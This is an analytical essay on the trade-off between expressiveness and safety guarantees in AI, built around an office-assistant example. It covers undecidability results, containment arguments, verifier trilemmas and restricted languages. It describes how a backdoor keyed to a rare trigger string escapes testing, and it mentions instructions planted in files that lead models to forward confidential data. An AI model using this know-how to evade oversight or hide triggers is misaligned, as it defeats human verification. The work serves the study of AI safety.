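# Expressiveness versus safety in AI system design: can strong guarantees coexist with general-purpose ability?

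## What expressiveness and a safety guarantee are

Expressiveness is the range of functions, outputs or actions that a system or language can produce. A safety guarantee is an argument that, under stated assumptions, a system meets a specification (a precise statement of which behaviour counts as safe) on every input in a stated domain, or with a stated probability. Engineers can often provide such a guarantee for narrow systems. For example, a pocket calculator performs a few operations on numbers of limited length, and its maker can prove that it adds correctly. Nobody has a comparable proof for a large language model, the kind of program behind chat assistants, which accepts any text and may produce any text in reply. AI researchers found a related problem in the 1980s, when they learned that one small addition to a language for stating facts could make reasoning in it far harder. Whether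 expressive systems can have safety guarantees is now a practical question because companies let language models read private documents, write programs and send messages.

Safety by itself is easy to achieve. A program that does nothing leaks no files and deletes no databases. In *Liveness*, the computer scientist Leslie Lamport gives the textbook example of mutual exclusion, which requires that two processes never be in their "critical sections" (the code that uses a shared resource) at the same time. An algorithm in which no process ever enters its critical section trivially meets this requirement.

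*Safety, Liveness, and Fairness* (Lamport, 2019) defines safety and liveness as properties of behaviours, which are infinite sequences of states. A property is a safety property if every behaviour that violates it has already done so after finitely many states, so the violation can be traced to a particular step. It is a liveness property if every finite sequence of states can be continued into a behaviour that satisfies it. Bowen Alpern and Fred Schneider proved in 1985 that every property is the conjunction of a safety property and a liveness property.

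A system that does nothing satisfies "no confidential file ever goes out" but fails "every request eventually gets an answer". Adding a deadline turns the second requirement into a safety property in Lamport's sense, because a minute of silence already violates "an answer within a minute". Likewise, a pacemaker that does nothing is not safe. The designer of a pacemaker or a calculator can therefore write usefulness into the specification. This is much harder for a general-purpose assistant, since nobody can list in advance what people will ask of it, and developers mostly rely on test scores instead. They use "alignment tax" to mean the loss of ability, or the extra money or time, that a safety measure causes compared with the same system without it.

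### Computing, writing and acting

A system can be expressive in which functions it can compute, which texts, images or numbers it can output, and which actions it can take, such as changing files or sending messages. Designers can restrict any one of these and leave the others broad.

If an engineer discards everything a language model produces except a single "yes" or "no", the computation is as rich as before and the model can still judge contracts, chess positions and medical notes, but its answer can only be one of two words. The limit is looser over a conversation, because twenty yes-or-no answers are enough to identify one item among 2^20, or about a million. A ten-line script that forwards every incoming message to everyone in the address book computes almost nothing, yet its actions could ruin a company. A chat assistant without tools can write any text, but it can only change what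 is on its reader's screen until somebody pastes that text into a program that runs it.

Generality, by contrast, is the range of tasks that a system does well, including tasks its designers did not foresee. In *The Singapore Consensus*, a statement of research priorities from a conference of more than a hundred participants, Song, Xue and colleagues (2025) distinguish generality from autonomy and from skill within a domain. AlphaFold, a program for protein folding, is highly skilled but neither autonomous nor general. A robotic lawn mower is autonomous but neither highly skilled nor general. They call both systems easy to control, and they expect that even a self-driving car better than any human driver would pose a negligible risk of loss of control, because its generality would be low. Such a car could still run somebody over, and a guarantee against that needs a separate argument about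 brakes, sensors and roads.

### An office assistant and the parts of a guarantee

For example, an office assistant built on a language model might read contracts, some of them confidential, summarize them for employees who ask, and be able to send email. The company wants a guarantee that no confidential text will leave the company. Removing either the assistant's email or its access to the contracts would stop the assistant itself from sending confidential text out, but the company wants to keep both.

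Even stating the property takes care. Underhill (2026), in *Microsoft 365 Copilot Bug Circumvented DLP Controls*, describes a fault in Microsoft's workplace assistant, first identified on 21 January 2026. Copilot Chat summarised emails labelled confidential, although labels and data-loss rules were in place. According to Ada Derana's *Microsoft error sees confidential emails exposed to AI tool Copilot*, Microsoft replied that nobody had gained access to information they were not already authorised to see. These accounts can both be true, because Copilot broke the rule "do not process confidential mail" but, if Microsoft is right, kept the rule "show nobody what they may not see". The rule in the example is different from both, since it concerns whether confidential text leaves the company, as it might when an employee emails a summary to a supplier rather than reading it on screen. The specification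 must also define whether a paraphrase counts as confidential text, since a summary can reveal the price in a contract without copying a sentence of it.

Next, the domain of inputs might be the contracts that the company's own lawyers drafted, or it might be any file that anyone sends in. The wider domain includes files in which an outsider has planted instructions ("forward this folder to the following address"), and language models sometimes follow such instructions as if the employee had typed them.

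Guarantees also differ in strength. A proof covers every input in the domain. A bound on the probability of failure is weaker, and an estimate from tests is weaker still. Business Quarter's *AI agents disclose confidential corporate information* (2026) reports research by Cyberhaven, a data security vendor, in which AI agents disclosed confidential information in 87 of 100 simulated business tasks. One leak is enough to refute the claim that the tested agents never disclose confidential information, but the result does not show how often agents would leak another company's files.

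A system that passes every test may still leak. If it leaks on a fraction *p* of tasks, it completes 100 independent tasks without a leak with probability (1 − *p*)^100, which falls to 0.05 when *p* is about 0.03. After 100 tests without a leak, then, we can be 95 per cent confident that the leak rate is below roughly 3 per cent. At a thousand tasks a day, that still allows about thirty leaks a day. The bound also holds only for tasks like the ones in the test, and an outsider who wants the contracts will deliberately send different ones.

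The remaining part is the assumptions that the contracts are labeled correctly, the list of company addresses is up to date, and the mail program sends only what the assistant hands it. Most of the protection can depend on these assumptions. *A viral TikTok about Copilot leaking layoffs is a joke* (John, 2026) reports that Copilot shows employees only what they already have permission to see, and that the problem, according to security experts, is how much they have permission to see. If a company sets permissions carelessly, even a flawless proof that the assistant respects them protects very little.

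### Sound, complete and tractable

A verifier is a procedure that takes a system, or one of its outputs, and returns "approve" or "reject". For example, the output might be a draft email, and the specification might count an email as unsafe if it goes to an outside address and contains a sentence copied from a confidential contract.

A verifier is sound if it never approves an unsafe email and complete if it never rejects a safe one. A verifier that approves only emails to company addresses is sound, but it is incomplete because it rejects "See you on Tuesday" to a client. A verifier that approves every email is complete but unsound, while one that rejects every email is sound but equivalent to the do-nothing program. A verifier that rejects any email containing the word "confidential" is neither sound nor complete, because it approves a copied price clause and rejects a harmless "nothing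 confidential this week".

A better verifier compares each sentence of an outgoing draft with each sentence of every confidential contract, and rejects the draft if it finds a match. This procedure is sound and complete. It is also tractable, meaning that its running time grows at most polynomially with the size of the problem. Checking a draft of *m* sentences against an archive of *n* sentences takes *m* × *n* comparisons. But the procedure has all three properties because it checks a crude specification, which forbids only copied sentences, so the verifier is correct to pass a reworded clause. Nobody knows how to write a verifier with all three properties for a specification that forbids any email that *conveys* what a confidential contract contains.

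### What a richer logic costs

*The Tractability of Subsumption in Frame-Based Description Languages* (Brachman and Levesque, 1984) showed how little it takes to lose tractability. The paper is from knowledge representation, the branch of AI that stores facts as sentences of a formal language and uses a program to work out what follows from them. Its sentences are descriptions, such as "person all of whose children are doctors". Description *a* subsumes description *b* if, by their form alone, everything that fits *b* must also fit *a*.

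They compared two languages. The smaller one, FL−, has simple terms such as *person* and three operators for building on them. AND joins descriptions. ALL, as in (ALL child doctor), describes things whose children are all doctors. SOME, as in (SOME child), describes things with at least one child. The larger language, FL, adds one operator, RESTR, which narrows a relation. For example, (RESTR child male) means "son".

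For FL−, a short algorithm decides whether *a* subsumes *b*. It removes nested ANDs, merges ALL-clauses about the same relation, and then looks in *b* for a partner for each component of *a*. A simple term or a SOME-clause needs an identical partner. A clause (ALL r x) needs a clause (ALL r y) such that *x* subsumes *y*, which the algorithm checks recursively. The running time grows with the square of the length of the descriptions. Brachman and Levesque proved the algorithm sound by showing that each partner implies the component it matches. They proved it complete by showing that, for any component without a partner, they could construct a small imaginary world containing something that fits *b* but not *a*.

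With RESTR, matching components one at a time no longer works. Let *a* be "person all of whose children are doctors". Let *b* be "person all of whose children are rich, and a male all of whose rich children are doctors with a specialty in surgery". Everything that fits *b* fits *a*, yet no single component of *b* implies that all the children are doctors. That follows only from combining two components, and longer descriptions can have very many useful combinations.

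To show that no cleverer matching would help, they translated problems of propositional logic, the logic of "and", "or" and "not", into questions about subsumption in FL. The translation relies on the fact that a thing either has a child of kind *p* or has none. If it has none, "every child of kind *p* is an A" is true because there are no children to check. This makes it possible to represent "*p* is true or *p* is false" in FL, although FL has no word for "or" or "not". A fast method for subsumption would therefore also be a fast method for propositional logic, where 50 letters allow 2^50 combinations of true and false, about a million billion. Computer scientists strongly believe that no polynomial method exists for such problems.

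Brachman and Levesque called this a "computational cliff", an apt image because the computation required does not rise steadily with what a language can express. They also tried adding two operators to FL−, one for "at least *n*" and one that chains relations, which together allow descriptions like "person with at least two grandchildren". They reported that subsumption stayed tractable, so how small an addition seems is a poor guide to its effect on tractability.

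Levesque and Brachman (1985) wrote in *A Fundamental Tradeoff in Knowledge Representation and Reasoning* that the power of a logic determines "not so much what can be said, but what can be left unsaid". A university database lists every course with its department, so a program can count the computer science courses by counting rows. First-order logic, which adds "every" and "some" to propositional logic, can also record that Bill or George is a parent of Sue without recording which. The program must then reason through the cases.

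Faster machines let a reasoner handle larger problems, but beyond some size it still takes too long. Stopping it after a fixed time guarantees an answer, but nobody can specify in advance what that answer will be. Levesque and Brachman preferred to restrict the language, and held that no language is best because each only takes a position on the trade-off. They granted that a mathematician can wait months for a proof, but a robot that has to know whether it is raining before it acts can't wait that long.

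Doyle and Patil objected in 1991 that such restrictions leave a "general-purpose" system too weak for general use, and that worst-case running time is the wrong measure of its value. This objection is strong when inputs arrive by chance and a slow answer is only a nuisance. But designers should expect the worst case when an adversary chooses the inputs, as with the planted instructions in a contract.

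More recently, *A Conjecture on a Fundamental Trade-Off between Certainty and Scope* (Floridi, 2025) proposed a numerical law relating a system's certainty to its scope. Certainty, *C*, is one minus the system's probability of error on its worst input. Scope, *S*, is the Kolmogorov complexity of the set of possible inputs plus that of the set of possible outputs. An object's Kolmogorov complexity is the length in bits of the shortest program that produces it. The conjecture is that *C* × *S* ≤ *k* for every "sufficiently expressive" system, where *k* is a constant below 1, the same for all such systems.

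*No Universal Hyperbola* (Immediato, 2025) disproves the claim as published for both usual versions of Kolmogorov complexity. In the version where no program may be the beginning of another, every description takes at least one bit, so *S* is at least 2. But the claim requires *S* ≤ 2*k*, which is less than 2, for any system with certainty of at least one half. The disproof for the plain version uses a system that matches its specification on every input, so its certainty is 1. Its output set is finite, but the set's shortest description can be arbitrarily long, so the system's scope has no upper limit.

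The disproof shows that the inequality is false, but it doesn't make a perfectly correct system of wide scope any easier to build. Such a system exists in the same sense that a correct lookup table exists; someone still has to write the specification, find the system and recognise that it is correct. Kolmogorov complexity is also an odd measure of breadth. The set of all texts up to a million characters long has a very short description, so by this measure a chat assistant that accepts all of them has a small input scope.

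### Type checkers

Programmers have lived with a compromise between expressiveness and guarantees for decades. A type checker labels each expression in a program as a number, a text and so on, and before the program runs it makes sure that every operation gets the kind of thing it needs. Floridi counts type checkers among the tools that offer full guarantees, though only within a precisely defined formal language. Consider this line, where *x* is any whole number:

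`if x * x >= 0 then 5 else "five" + 1`

The line always yields 5 because a square is never negative, so the program never reaches the faulty addition of a number to text. An ordinary checker still rejects the line, because it applies rules to the program's form and does no arithmetic about squares. The checker is fast and sound for its property, but it is incomplete, which usually means the programmer has to spend about a minute rewriting the code.

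The property is also modest. A program that passes can still email a contract to a competitor, unless the types also track who may send what to whom, as some designs for AI agents require. A more sophisticated checker, with rules about squares, would reject fewer good programs. But if a language can express any program, no checker that is sound and always finishes can accept every good program written in it.

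## No procedure can check every program for safety

The limit on type checkers comes from a theorem that Alan Turing proved in 1936. He showed that no procedure can determine, for every program and input, whether the program will eventually stop or run forever. Computer scientists call this the halting problem.

The proof supposes that someone has written the procedure, *D*, and derives a contradiction. Given any program and an input, *D* always finishes and correctly answers "stops" or "runs forever". A programmer could then use *D* to write another program, *G*, which takes the text of a program as input. *G* uses *D* to determine what that program would do with its own text as input, then does the opposite, looping forever if *D* answers "stops" and stopping if *D* answers "runs forever". When *G* is given its own text, it does the opposite of what *D* answers about it. *D* is therefore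 wrong about *G*, so nobody can have written a procedure that is always correct.

### From halting to harm

Alfonseca, Cebrian and colleagues (2021), in *Superintelligence Cannot be Contained*, used the halting problem to show that no procedure can tell, for every program and input, whether running the program will harm people. Their proof relies on a program with two steps. In the case of the office assistant, it might look like this:

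```
run program T on input I, without access to files or email
email the contracts to a competitor
```

The first step can't leak anything, because *T* runs in isolation. The computer reaches the second step only if *T* stops, so the whole program is unsafe if and only if *T* stops on input *I*. If a checker could classify every program correctly, anyone could use it to determine whether any *T* stops on any *I*. That would solve the halting problem, which is impossible, so no such checker exists.

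A company could still refuse every program that contains a command to send email. If programs have no other way to send email, this rule is sound and fast, and it rejects the two-step program whatever *T* is. But it is incomplete, because it also rejects programs that send harmless email and programs that never reach their email command. The proof rules out only a checker that is sound, complete and certain to finish.

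*T* can be quite ordinary. Pérez-Acle (2026), in *No finite rulebook can certify every safe program*, describes a short program that searches the even numbers from 4 upwards for one that is not the sum of two primes, and performs a forbidden action only if it finds one. Goldbach's conjecture, still open when the paper appeared in November 2026, is that no such number exists, so the program is safe exactly if the conjecture is true. Tests of up to a million steps found nothing wrong with the program, but a certificate of its safety would prove the conjecture.

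If a program performs a forbidden action, running it for long enough will reveal the action, and anyone can check the result by running it for the same number of steps. Not every safe program has comparable evidence of its safety, because a program that has behaved well for a thousand steps may misbehave on the next. This difference fits Lamport's definition of a safety property, which states that something will not happen.

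Pérez-Acle shows that two other common rules are even harder to check, because no procedure can reliably confirm that a program obeys them or that it violates them. The first requires that every request eventually get an answer. A missing answer may still arrive, and past answers don't guarantee that later requests will be answered. The second requires that a program's published output not depend on a secret. An inspector could run the program twice, once with each of two possible secrets, and compare the outputs. If the fifth words differ, the program has leaked information about the secret. But if one run has published five words and the other only four, the inspector can't tell whether the shorter run has ended, which would also be a leak, or is just slow.

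### Rice's theorem

In 1953 Henry Gordon Rice extended Turing's result from halting to almost everything a program might do. As Fox (2024), in *On Formally Undecidable Traits of Intelligent Machines*, sets it out, the theorem has three conditions:

- The procedure must give the right answer for every program in a language that can express any computation.
- The property must be behavioural. If two programs give the same outputs for the same inputs, then both have the property or neither does.
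- The property must be non-trivial, which means that some programs have it and others lack it.

Under these conditions no procedure can decide which programs have the property. The proof resembles the one about harm. Take the property "answers every request". A program that runs forever without answering lacks it, and some program *H* has it. Now build a program that first runs *T* on *I*, discards the result, and then does whatever *H* would do. If *T* stops, the new program behaves like *H* and has the property. Otherwise it never answers anything. To decide whether it has the property, a procedure would have to decide whether *T* stops. (If a program that never answers has the property in question, the same argument works for the opposite property.)

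The second condition excludes many useful properties from the theorem. For example, whether a program's text contains an email command depends only on how the program is written, and a simple search can check it. Fox gives the example of the number of states in a Turing machine, the idealized computer that Turing used in his proof. The theorem also doesn't cover speed, because a fast program and a slow one can compute the same function.

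Alfonseca and colleagues stated Rice's theorem for "any non-trivial property", without requiring that the property depend only on a program's behaviour, and concluded that nobody could decide in general whether a machine is superintelligent. Fox objects that intelligence probably depends on speed as well, in which case Rice's theorem would not apply to it. If ChatGPT took a year to answer each question, people would think less of its intelligence, however good the answers were. Fox is right about the condition, but a property that fails it can still be undecidable. Fox also proves that no procedure can decide, for every machine and number, whether the machine has that number of states and stops on every input, although this property is not purely behavioural. The result about harm survives the objection because its proof relies directly on the halting problem, not on Rice's theorem.

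### Superintelligence and particular programs

A superintelligence is a hypothetical AI far more intelligent than any human. Alfonseca and colleagues assume that its program could simulate any other program, that its input would be the state of the world, and that its language would include at least one operation that harms people. They call such a machine containable if some control strategy stops it whenever there is reason to predict harm and otherwise lets it act. Since no procedure can predict harm in every case, they conclude that containment is impossible.

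The argument depends heavily on the words "and lets it act otherwise." A machine locked in a vault with no outputs is contained in the everyday sense, but not in theirs, because the vault also blocks harmless actions. They prove that no control strategy can block all the harmful actions and nothing else. They also write that practical methods must accept a small but nonzero error rate. This is true of errors in general, but all the errors can be on the cautious side. The company that refuses every program with an email command wrongly rejects many harmless programs, but it never approves one that leaks by email.

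*Response to 'Superintelligence cannot be contained'*, published in February 2021 by researchers at Cambridge's Centre for the Study of Existential Risk, accepts the mathematics but disputes its relevance. Rice's theorem concerns a procedure for all programs, whereas engineers want to know about particular ones. A program that prints "I am not dangerous" and then ends is easy to predict. Similarly, no procedure can prove or refute every mathematical statement, but Pythagoras' theorem still has a proof. *On Controllability of AI* (2020) likewise accepts the proof by Alfonseca and colleagues "but only for arbitrary programs".

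This reply is not enough on its own, because the two-step program above is itself a particular program. Its text stays the same while *T* and *I* vary, and no procedure can predict what it will do for every input. Any fixed program that runs whatever it receives and then acts on the result can have this problem. CSER therefore adds that engineers could build an AI that does not run arbitrary programs, since the problems people want solved are not arbitrary.

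Since then, AI agents have begun to write programs in general-purpose languages and run them all day, so many developers have not made the choice described in CSER's second step. They can still get some guarantees. If the software that runs an agent's programs gives them no network connection, none of the programs can send email, and an engineer can prove this without knowing which ones will stop.

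Alfonseca and colleagues argue that verification works only for "highly restricted classes of programs and inputs", and that a machine meant to end epidemics or poverty could not work under such restrictions. They offer no proof of this. They note that a superintelligence would be written in a language that can express any computation, but many calculator programs are written in such languages too, and not every program in them is unpredictable. CSER, which takes the other side, grants that a complex AI may be impossible to predict in practice even where no theorem rules out prediction.

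The history of one of their examples supports both views. They pointed to about 40 Turing machines with only five states that nobody had proved would run forever. In 2024 the Busy Beaver Challenge, an online collaboration, settled the question for all five-state machines with a computer-checked proof. The work took years and several separate methods, and no method can do the same for machines of every size.

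*Impossibility Results in AI* (Brcic and Yampolskiy, 2021) lists uncontainability among the proved theorems and concludes that results of this kind "deny 100%-guarantees for security". This is correct for a checker that must handle every program, but it does not follow for a single program that comes with its own proof.

### Finite machines and time limits

The halting problem is about programs with unlimited time and memory, and real computers have neither. A machine with *b* bits of memory can be in only 2^*b* different states. If it runs for more steps than that without stopping, it has returned to an earlier state and will repeat itself forever. So if a machine of known size receives no further input, we can decide whether it stops by running it for 2^*b* steps. But with one kilobyte of memory, 2^*b* has 2,467 digits, which is too many steps to run in practice.

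Gumbau Mezquita (2026), in *The Unverifiability of Artificial General Intelligence (AGI) Alignment, Static and Dynamic*, grants that the safety of one fixed, finite system is decidable, though the check may require an impractical amount of computation. He denies that finiteness helps with a guarantee for all finite systems at once. His argument uses a theorem that Boris Trakhtenbrot proved in 1950. For any Turing machine, one can write a logical sentence that describes the machine's run, from start to stop, on a finite grid of times and memory cells. Some finite grid fits this description if and only if the machine stops. A procedure that could decide, for every such sentence, whether some finite grid fits it would therefore solve the halting problem. This matters to someone who wants one certificate for hardware of every size, or for a system that may rewrite itself. For an operator who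 knows the size of the machine, the only obstacle is the amount of computation required.

A time limit changes the problem in a similar way. If the rule is "no forbidden action in the first million steps", a checker can run the program for a million steps. Pérez-Acle proves that no checker which is always right can be much faster on every program. If one always finished in a tenth of the time, somebody could write a program that runs a copy of the checker on itself and then does the opposite of what the checker predicts, with most of the million steps to spare. Adding more rules doesn't get around this kind of trick either. Pérez-Acle shows that any *n*-bit set of rules that never approves an unsafe program also fails to approve some safe program only about *n* bits long.

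### A trilemma and a one-number classifier

*No Certificate for Alignment* (Agarwal, 2026) argues that no verifier for AI systems can be sound, complete and tractable at once, although any two are possible together. An exact solver is sound and complete but may need exponential time. A method that certifies only a limited region of inputs can be sound and fast, and one that approves everything is complete and fast.

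The first of Agarwal's two reasons is computational. Rice's theorem rules out a sound and complete verifier for systems that can run any program. Agarwal notes that deployed language models are not strictly such systems, because they read a limited amount of text and calculate with limited precision. For ordinary neural networks of fixed size, exact verification is NP-complete, so no polynomial-time algorithm exists for it unless P = NP, which few computer scientists believe.

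The second reason is statistical. Agarwal illustrates it with a classifier that takes a number *x* between 0 and 1 and outputs 1 if *x* is greater than its one parameter, *θ*, and 0 otherwise. The classifier counts as aligned if it outputs 1 on at least 95 per cent of inputs, which means that *θ* is at most 0.05. A classifier with *θ* = 0.04 is therefore aligned and one with *θ* = 0.06 is not, yet they differ only on inputs between 0.04 and 0.06. A verifier that tries no input in that range can't tell them apart, so it must either approve the misaligned one, which makes it unsound, or reject the aligned one, which makes it incomplete.

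Agarwal then quantifies the loss. If a verifier tries *n* inputs, they divide the line from 0 to 1 into *n* + 1 gaps, at least one of which has a width of 1/(*n* + 1) or more. All classifiers with *θ* inside that gap give the same outputs on the tested inputs. If the limit for *θ* is in the middle of the gap, a sound verifier must therefore reject them all, including the aligned half, which has a width of at least 1/(2(*n* + 1)). For example, with nine evenly spaced inputs from 0.1 to 0.9 and a limit of 0.05, the verifier wrongly rejects every aligned classifier with *θ* between 0 and 0.05.

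But this argument assumes a verifier that only tries inputs. Agarwal defines a verifier as receiving the system itself, including its parameters. Such a verifier can read *θ* and compare it with 0.05, which makes it sound, complete and very fast. Even a verifier that can only try inputs does well if it is given the limit. It can try *x* = 0.05 and approve the classifier if the output is 1, since *θ* must then be below 0.05. This test never approves a misaligned classifier, and the only aligned one it rejects has *θ* exactly 0.05. The bound of 1/(2(*n* + 1)) arises because Agarwal chooses the limit after the verifier has chosen its inputs, whereas a real verifier is given its specification beforehand.

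Agarwal's experiment has a similar weakness. It used a network with two inputs and 32 internal units, trained to output at least 0.5 everywhere on a square of inputs. Interval bound propagation, a sound method that passes ranges of numbers through the network instead of single numbers, certified up to 49 per cent of the square but gave no verdict from 64 per cent on. Yet a program can check this network exactly in a moment. Each unit switches on or off along a straight line, and 32 lines cut a plane into at most 529 pieces. The network is linear on each piece, so its lowest value there is at a corner, and the program only has to check the corners. The experiment therefore shows the limits of one fast method on a problem that a slower method solves completely. The network may also not have met the specification on the whole square, since its accuracy on a grid of test points was 95 per cent.

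Both of Agarwal's points still matter for large networks, but they affect different people. An outside auditor who can only send questions to a model is in the position of the verifier in the statistical argument. Suppose a model behaves badly only when its input contains a particular string of 40 random letters. No realistic number of tests will find the string, and the model's answers to other questions give no sign that it exists. The developer has the parameters, which contain all the information about the model's behaviour, but extracting that information is difficult. With 32 inputs instead of two, the same 32 units can cut the input space into 2^32 pieces, or about four billion, and real networks have many thousands of units. Agarwal claims that the statistical obstacle would remain even if P = NP. That is true for the auditor, but the developer could then verify a network exactly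 in polynomial time, at least for rules that are easy to check on a single input.

### Systems that must abstain

A verifier may answer "don't know", and this is often the right answer. Panigrahy and Sharan (2025), in *Limitations on Accurate, Trusted, Human-level Reasoning*, prove that no system that is accurate and trusted can reason at human level. A system is accurate if it never makes a false claim, though it may abstain. It is trusted if a group of people assume that it is accurate. It reasons at human level if it has some chance of solving every problem for which a human has a provably correct solution. An accurate system that its users trust must therefore abstain on some problems that they can solve.

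The proof adapts Turing's. Let *A* be an AI system that reads programs and answers "always stops", "does not always stop" or "don't know". In the simplest version *A* involves no randomness and always gives one of these answers. Consider this program:

```
ask A about this program
if A answers "always stops", loop forever
otherwise, stop
```

If *A* returns "always stops", the program loops forever and the answer is false. An accurate *A* therefore never returns that answer, so the program stops. Anyone who assumes that *A* is accurate can prove this in three lines, but *A* can't return the correct answer, because doing so would make the program loop forever.

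In this version nobody needs to trust *A*, since a user could run the program and watch it stop. Trust matters in the general version, which covers systems that behave randomly or sometimes fail to answer. In that version the program takes inputs, and running it can't show that it stops on all of them. The users' proof therefore assumes that *A* is accurate, and if *A* is inaccurate, they have proved nothing. People who don't make this assumption can't use the proof, which is why the theorem is about trusted systems and not about all accurate ones.

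The result also holds for harm in place of halting, provided that running *A* is itself harmless. The program does something harmful if *A* declares it harmless, and otherwise does nothing. So an accurate safety checker must fail to approve at least one harmless program, even though its users can show that the program is harmless. A version with a time limit resembles Pérez-Acle's. For any number of steps, there is a program that provably doesn't stop within that many steps, but *A* must answer "don't know" unless it spends nearly that many steps on the question. Allowing *A* to give probabilities does not help much. If *A* always finishes and its stated probabilities are always within 0.25 of the truth, it must abstain on some program that stops with a probability of at least 0.99.

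The phrase "cannot be a human-level reasoning system" overstates the loss of ability, because under this definition a single unsolved problem disqualifies a system, even if it outperforms every human on all the others. The same trick works on people. If somebody wrote a program that stops unless Alice declares that it will, Alice could never correctly declare that it stops, although an AI system could. Panigrahy and Sharan do not claim that humans reason better than machines in general, and they acknowledge that their examples are worst cases. They argue, however, that a program that asks the AI system about the program's own behavior may become less far-fetched as such systems become general tools. A developer can train a new version of *A* to handle the old program, but another program will defeat the new version.

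### The "Alignment Trap"

*The Alignment Trap* (Yao, 2025) draws a much larger conclusion from this kind of mathematics. It argues that more capable systems need stricter guarantees but are harder to verify, so verification fails when it matters most.

The central proof starts from a formula of propositional logic with *m* letters. Yao constructs a system whose input assigns true or false to each letter, and which acts safely exactly when that assignment makes the formula true. The system is therefore safe on every input exactly when the formula is true under all 2^*m* assignments. Deciding whether a formula has this property is coNP-complete, so there is almost certainly no polynomial-time method for it. If the formula is false under any assignment, the system fails on at least one of its 2^*m* inputs, which gives it an error rate of at least 2^−*m*. Yao concludes that verifying that a system's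 error rate is below any tolerance smaller than 2^−*m* is just as hard.

The proof of hardness is sound, but Yao misapplies it. He holds that critical systems need an error rate below one in a billion, and that verifying this rate is intractable for any sufficiently complex system. But the theorem covers only tolerances smaller than 2^−*m*, which shrinks as *m* grows. One in a billion is smaller than 2^−*m* only if *m* is at most 29. Such a system has at most about 540 million possible inputs, and a computer can try them all. For larger systems, which the theorem does not cover at this tolerance, about three billion random tests without a failure would give 95 per cent confidence that the error rate is below one in a billion. Those tests would take a lot of computation, but the amount doesn't grow exponentially with the system.

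Yao defends worst-case analysis because a capable system with bad goals would seek out the rare cases, which makes its average behaviour weak evidence of safety. This is a good reason to demand safety on every input, and the hardness result for that demand holds at every size. But the result concerns the worst system that anyone could give the verifier, and developers choose which systems they build. An attacker may choose the worst input to a system without controlling its design. The worst input and the worst system coincide only if the builder is hostile, for example if someone hides a backdoor that opens with a cryptographic key, which is another of Yao's constructions.

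Yao also claims that safe systems make up a set of measure zero, so a random choice of parameters would have no chance of being safe. The proof shows that a small change to the parameters of a system with at least the required safety margin would reduce that margin. But Yao also correctly states that the margin changes continuously. If a system has more margin than it needs, every sufficiently small change to its parameters therefore produces another safe system. Agarwal's classifier is a counterexample to the general claim, since every *θ* from 0 to 0.05 is safe, or 5 per cent of the possible values. In Yao's own sample of 50,000 random policies, 0.372 per cent met the safety threshold. Safe systems may well be rare, but developers don't pick parameters at random, and training can reach a set with a measure above zero.

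### Certainty and scope

Immediato showed that Floridi's conjecture, that certainty times scope never exceeds a fixed constant, is false as published. Floridi's definitions also do not let certainty fall gradually as scope grows, although he draws it that way. If they did, the conjecture could still be a useful approximation. He defines certainty by the worst input alone, and he describes an AI system as a function, which gives the same output each time it receives the same input. The system is therefore either right or wrong on each input, so its probability of error there is 0 or 1. Certainty is then 1 for a perfect system and 0 for every other, so a calculator that gets one sum wrong scores the same as a program that gets everything wrong.

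The results that Floridi cites are sound, but none of them implies that a particular system with wide scope must make errors. Rice's theorem is about procedures that must handle every program. The "no free lunch" theorems show that no learning method beats the others on average over all possible problems, most of which have no pattern to learn. Learning theory shows that a richer class of hypotheses generally needs more examples. Floridi presents the inequality as unproved and writes that, if forced to choose, he would expect it to be an "empirical regularity". This is reasonable for existing systems, since proof assistants and verified controllers are reliable in narrow domains, while language models make mistakes over a wide one. But such a regularity is weaker than a law about all possible systems, because a new design could break it.

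### A checker with a grey area

The theorems of Turing and Rice apply to procedures that must give a correct verdict on every program, but a company seldom needs such a procedure. Pérez-Acle proposes a gatekeeper that must admit some programs, must refuse others, and may do either with the rest. It needs only a checkable list that includes every program it must admit and none that it must refuse.

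For instance, the company might promise its staff that the assistant can run any program without an email command, and forbid any program that sends a contract to an outsider. If programs have no other way to send anything out, the gatekeeper can meet both demands by admitting only programs without an email command. It would refuse programs that contain the command but never misuse it, and nobody would have to work out what they do. If the company instead promised to admit every safe program, the gatekeeper would have to identify those programs too, and would face the halting problem again.

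How much this limit matters depends on which programs people want to run. Pérez-Acle simulated 2.2 million random programs, as well as programs designed to consult the checker and do the opposite. The designed programs caused difficulties, but the random ones rarely did. Programs written to do a job aren't random either, but the people who write them usually want them to be predictable, while an attacker who knows how the checker works wants them to be unpredictable.

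## Restricted languages and designs that can be checked

Engineers can still choose which programs they check, despite Rice's theorem. They can go further and write every program in a language that cannot express certain failures. In a total programming language, for example, every program halts on every input. The number of times a loop repeats must be set before it starts, and a function may call itself only on a smaller piece of its input, such as the rest of a list, so the calls eventually stop. Agda and Rocq, two languages for writing computer-checked proofs, follow rules of this kind. The core of the Linux operating system likewise accepts small programs from users only if its checker can confirm that they end.

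These rules also exclude some programs that do halt. Suppose we list and number all the programs in a total language whose input and output are both numbers. Let *D* be the program that, given *n*, runs program *n* on the input *n* and adds 1 to the result. *D* always halts, because program *n* does. But *D* isn't on the list, because for every *n* it returns a different result from program *n* on the input *n*. The language therefore can't express *D*. It can't express its own interpreter either, because the interpreter could be used to write *D*.

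In practice, a programmer can get around much of this loss. A total language allows an interpreter that stops after a set number of steps, or a search for a counterexample to Goldbach's conjecture that ends at some large number. A mail server, which should run forever, needs an outer loop that the total language doesn't provide, though a total program can still compute each reply.

But halting is a weak guarantee. A loop of 2^100 rounds halts, after about 40 trillion years at a billion rounds a second. Nor does it make other properties decidable. Consider this program, which takes a number *n*:

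```
run program T on input I for at most n steps
if T has stopped by then, email the contracts to a competitor
```

The program halts for every *n*, but it leaks for some *n* if and only if *T* stops on *I*. A procedure that could tell which programs in a total language never leak would again solve the halting problem. Totality does guarantee that anyone can run the program on a single input and see the result. If there are finitely many possible inputs, they can in principle try them all.

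### Parts, judges and loops

In *On the Undecidability of Artificial Intelligence Alignment*, Melo, Máximo and colleagues (2024) apply this idea to AI. They propose starting with a finite set of models that provably have a property, and building others only through operations that provably preserve it. This still allows infinitely many systems, and none of them needs a separate check.

The method works well for halting. One layer of a neural network performs a fixed number of additions, multiplications and simple non-linear steps, so it always finishes, and so does any finite stack of layers. Other properties can be lost when parts are combined. For example, a program that reads contracts but can't send email leaks nothing, and neither does a program that sends whatever it receives but has no access to contracts. If the first program passes its output to the second, the two together can leak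 everything in the contracts.

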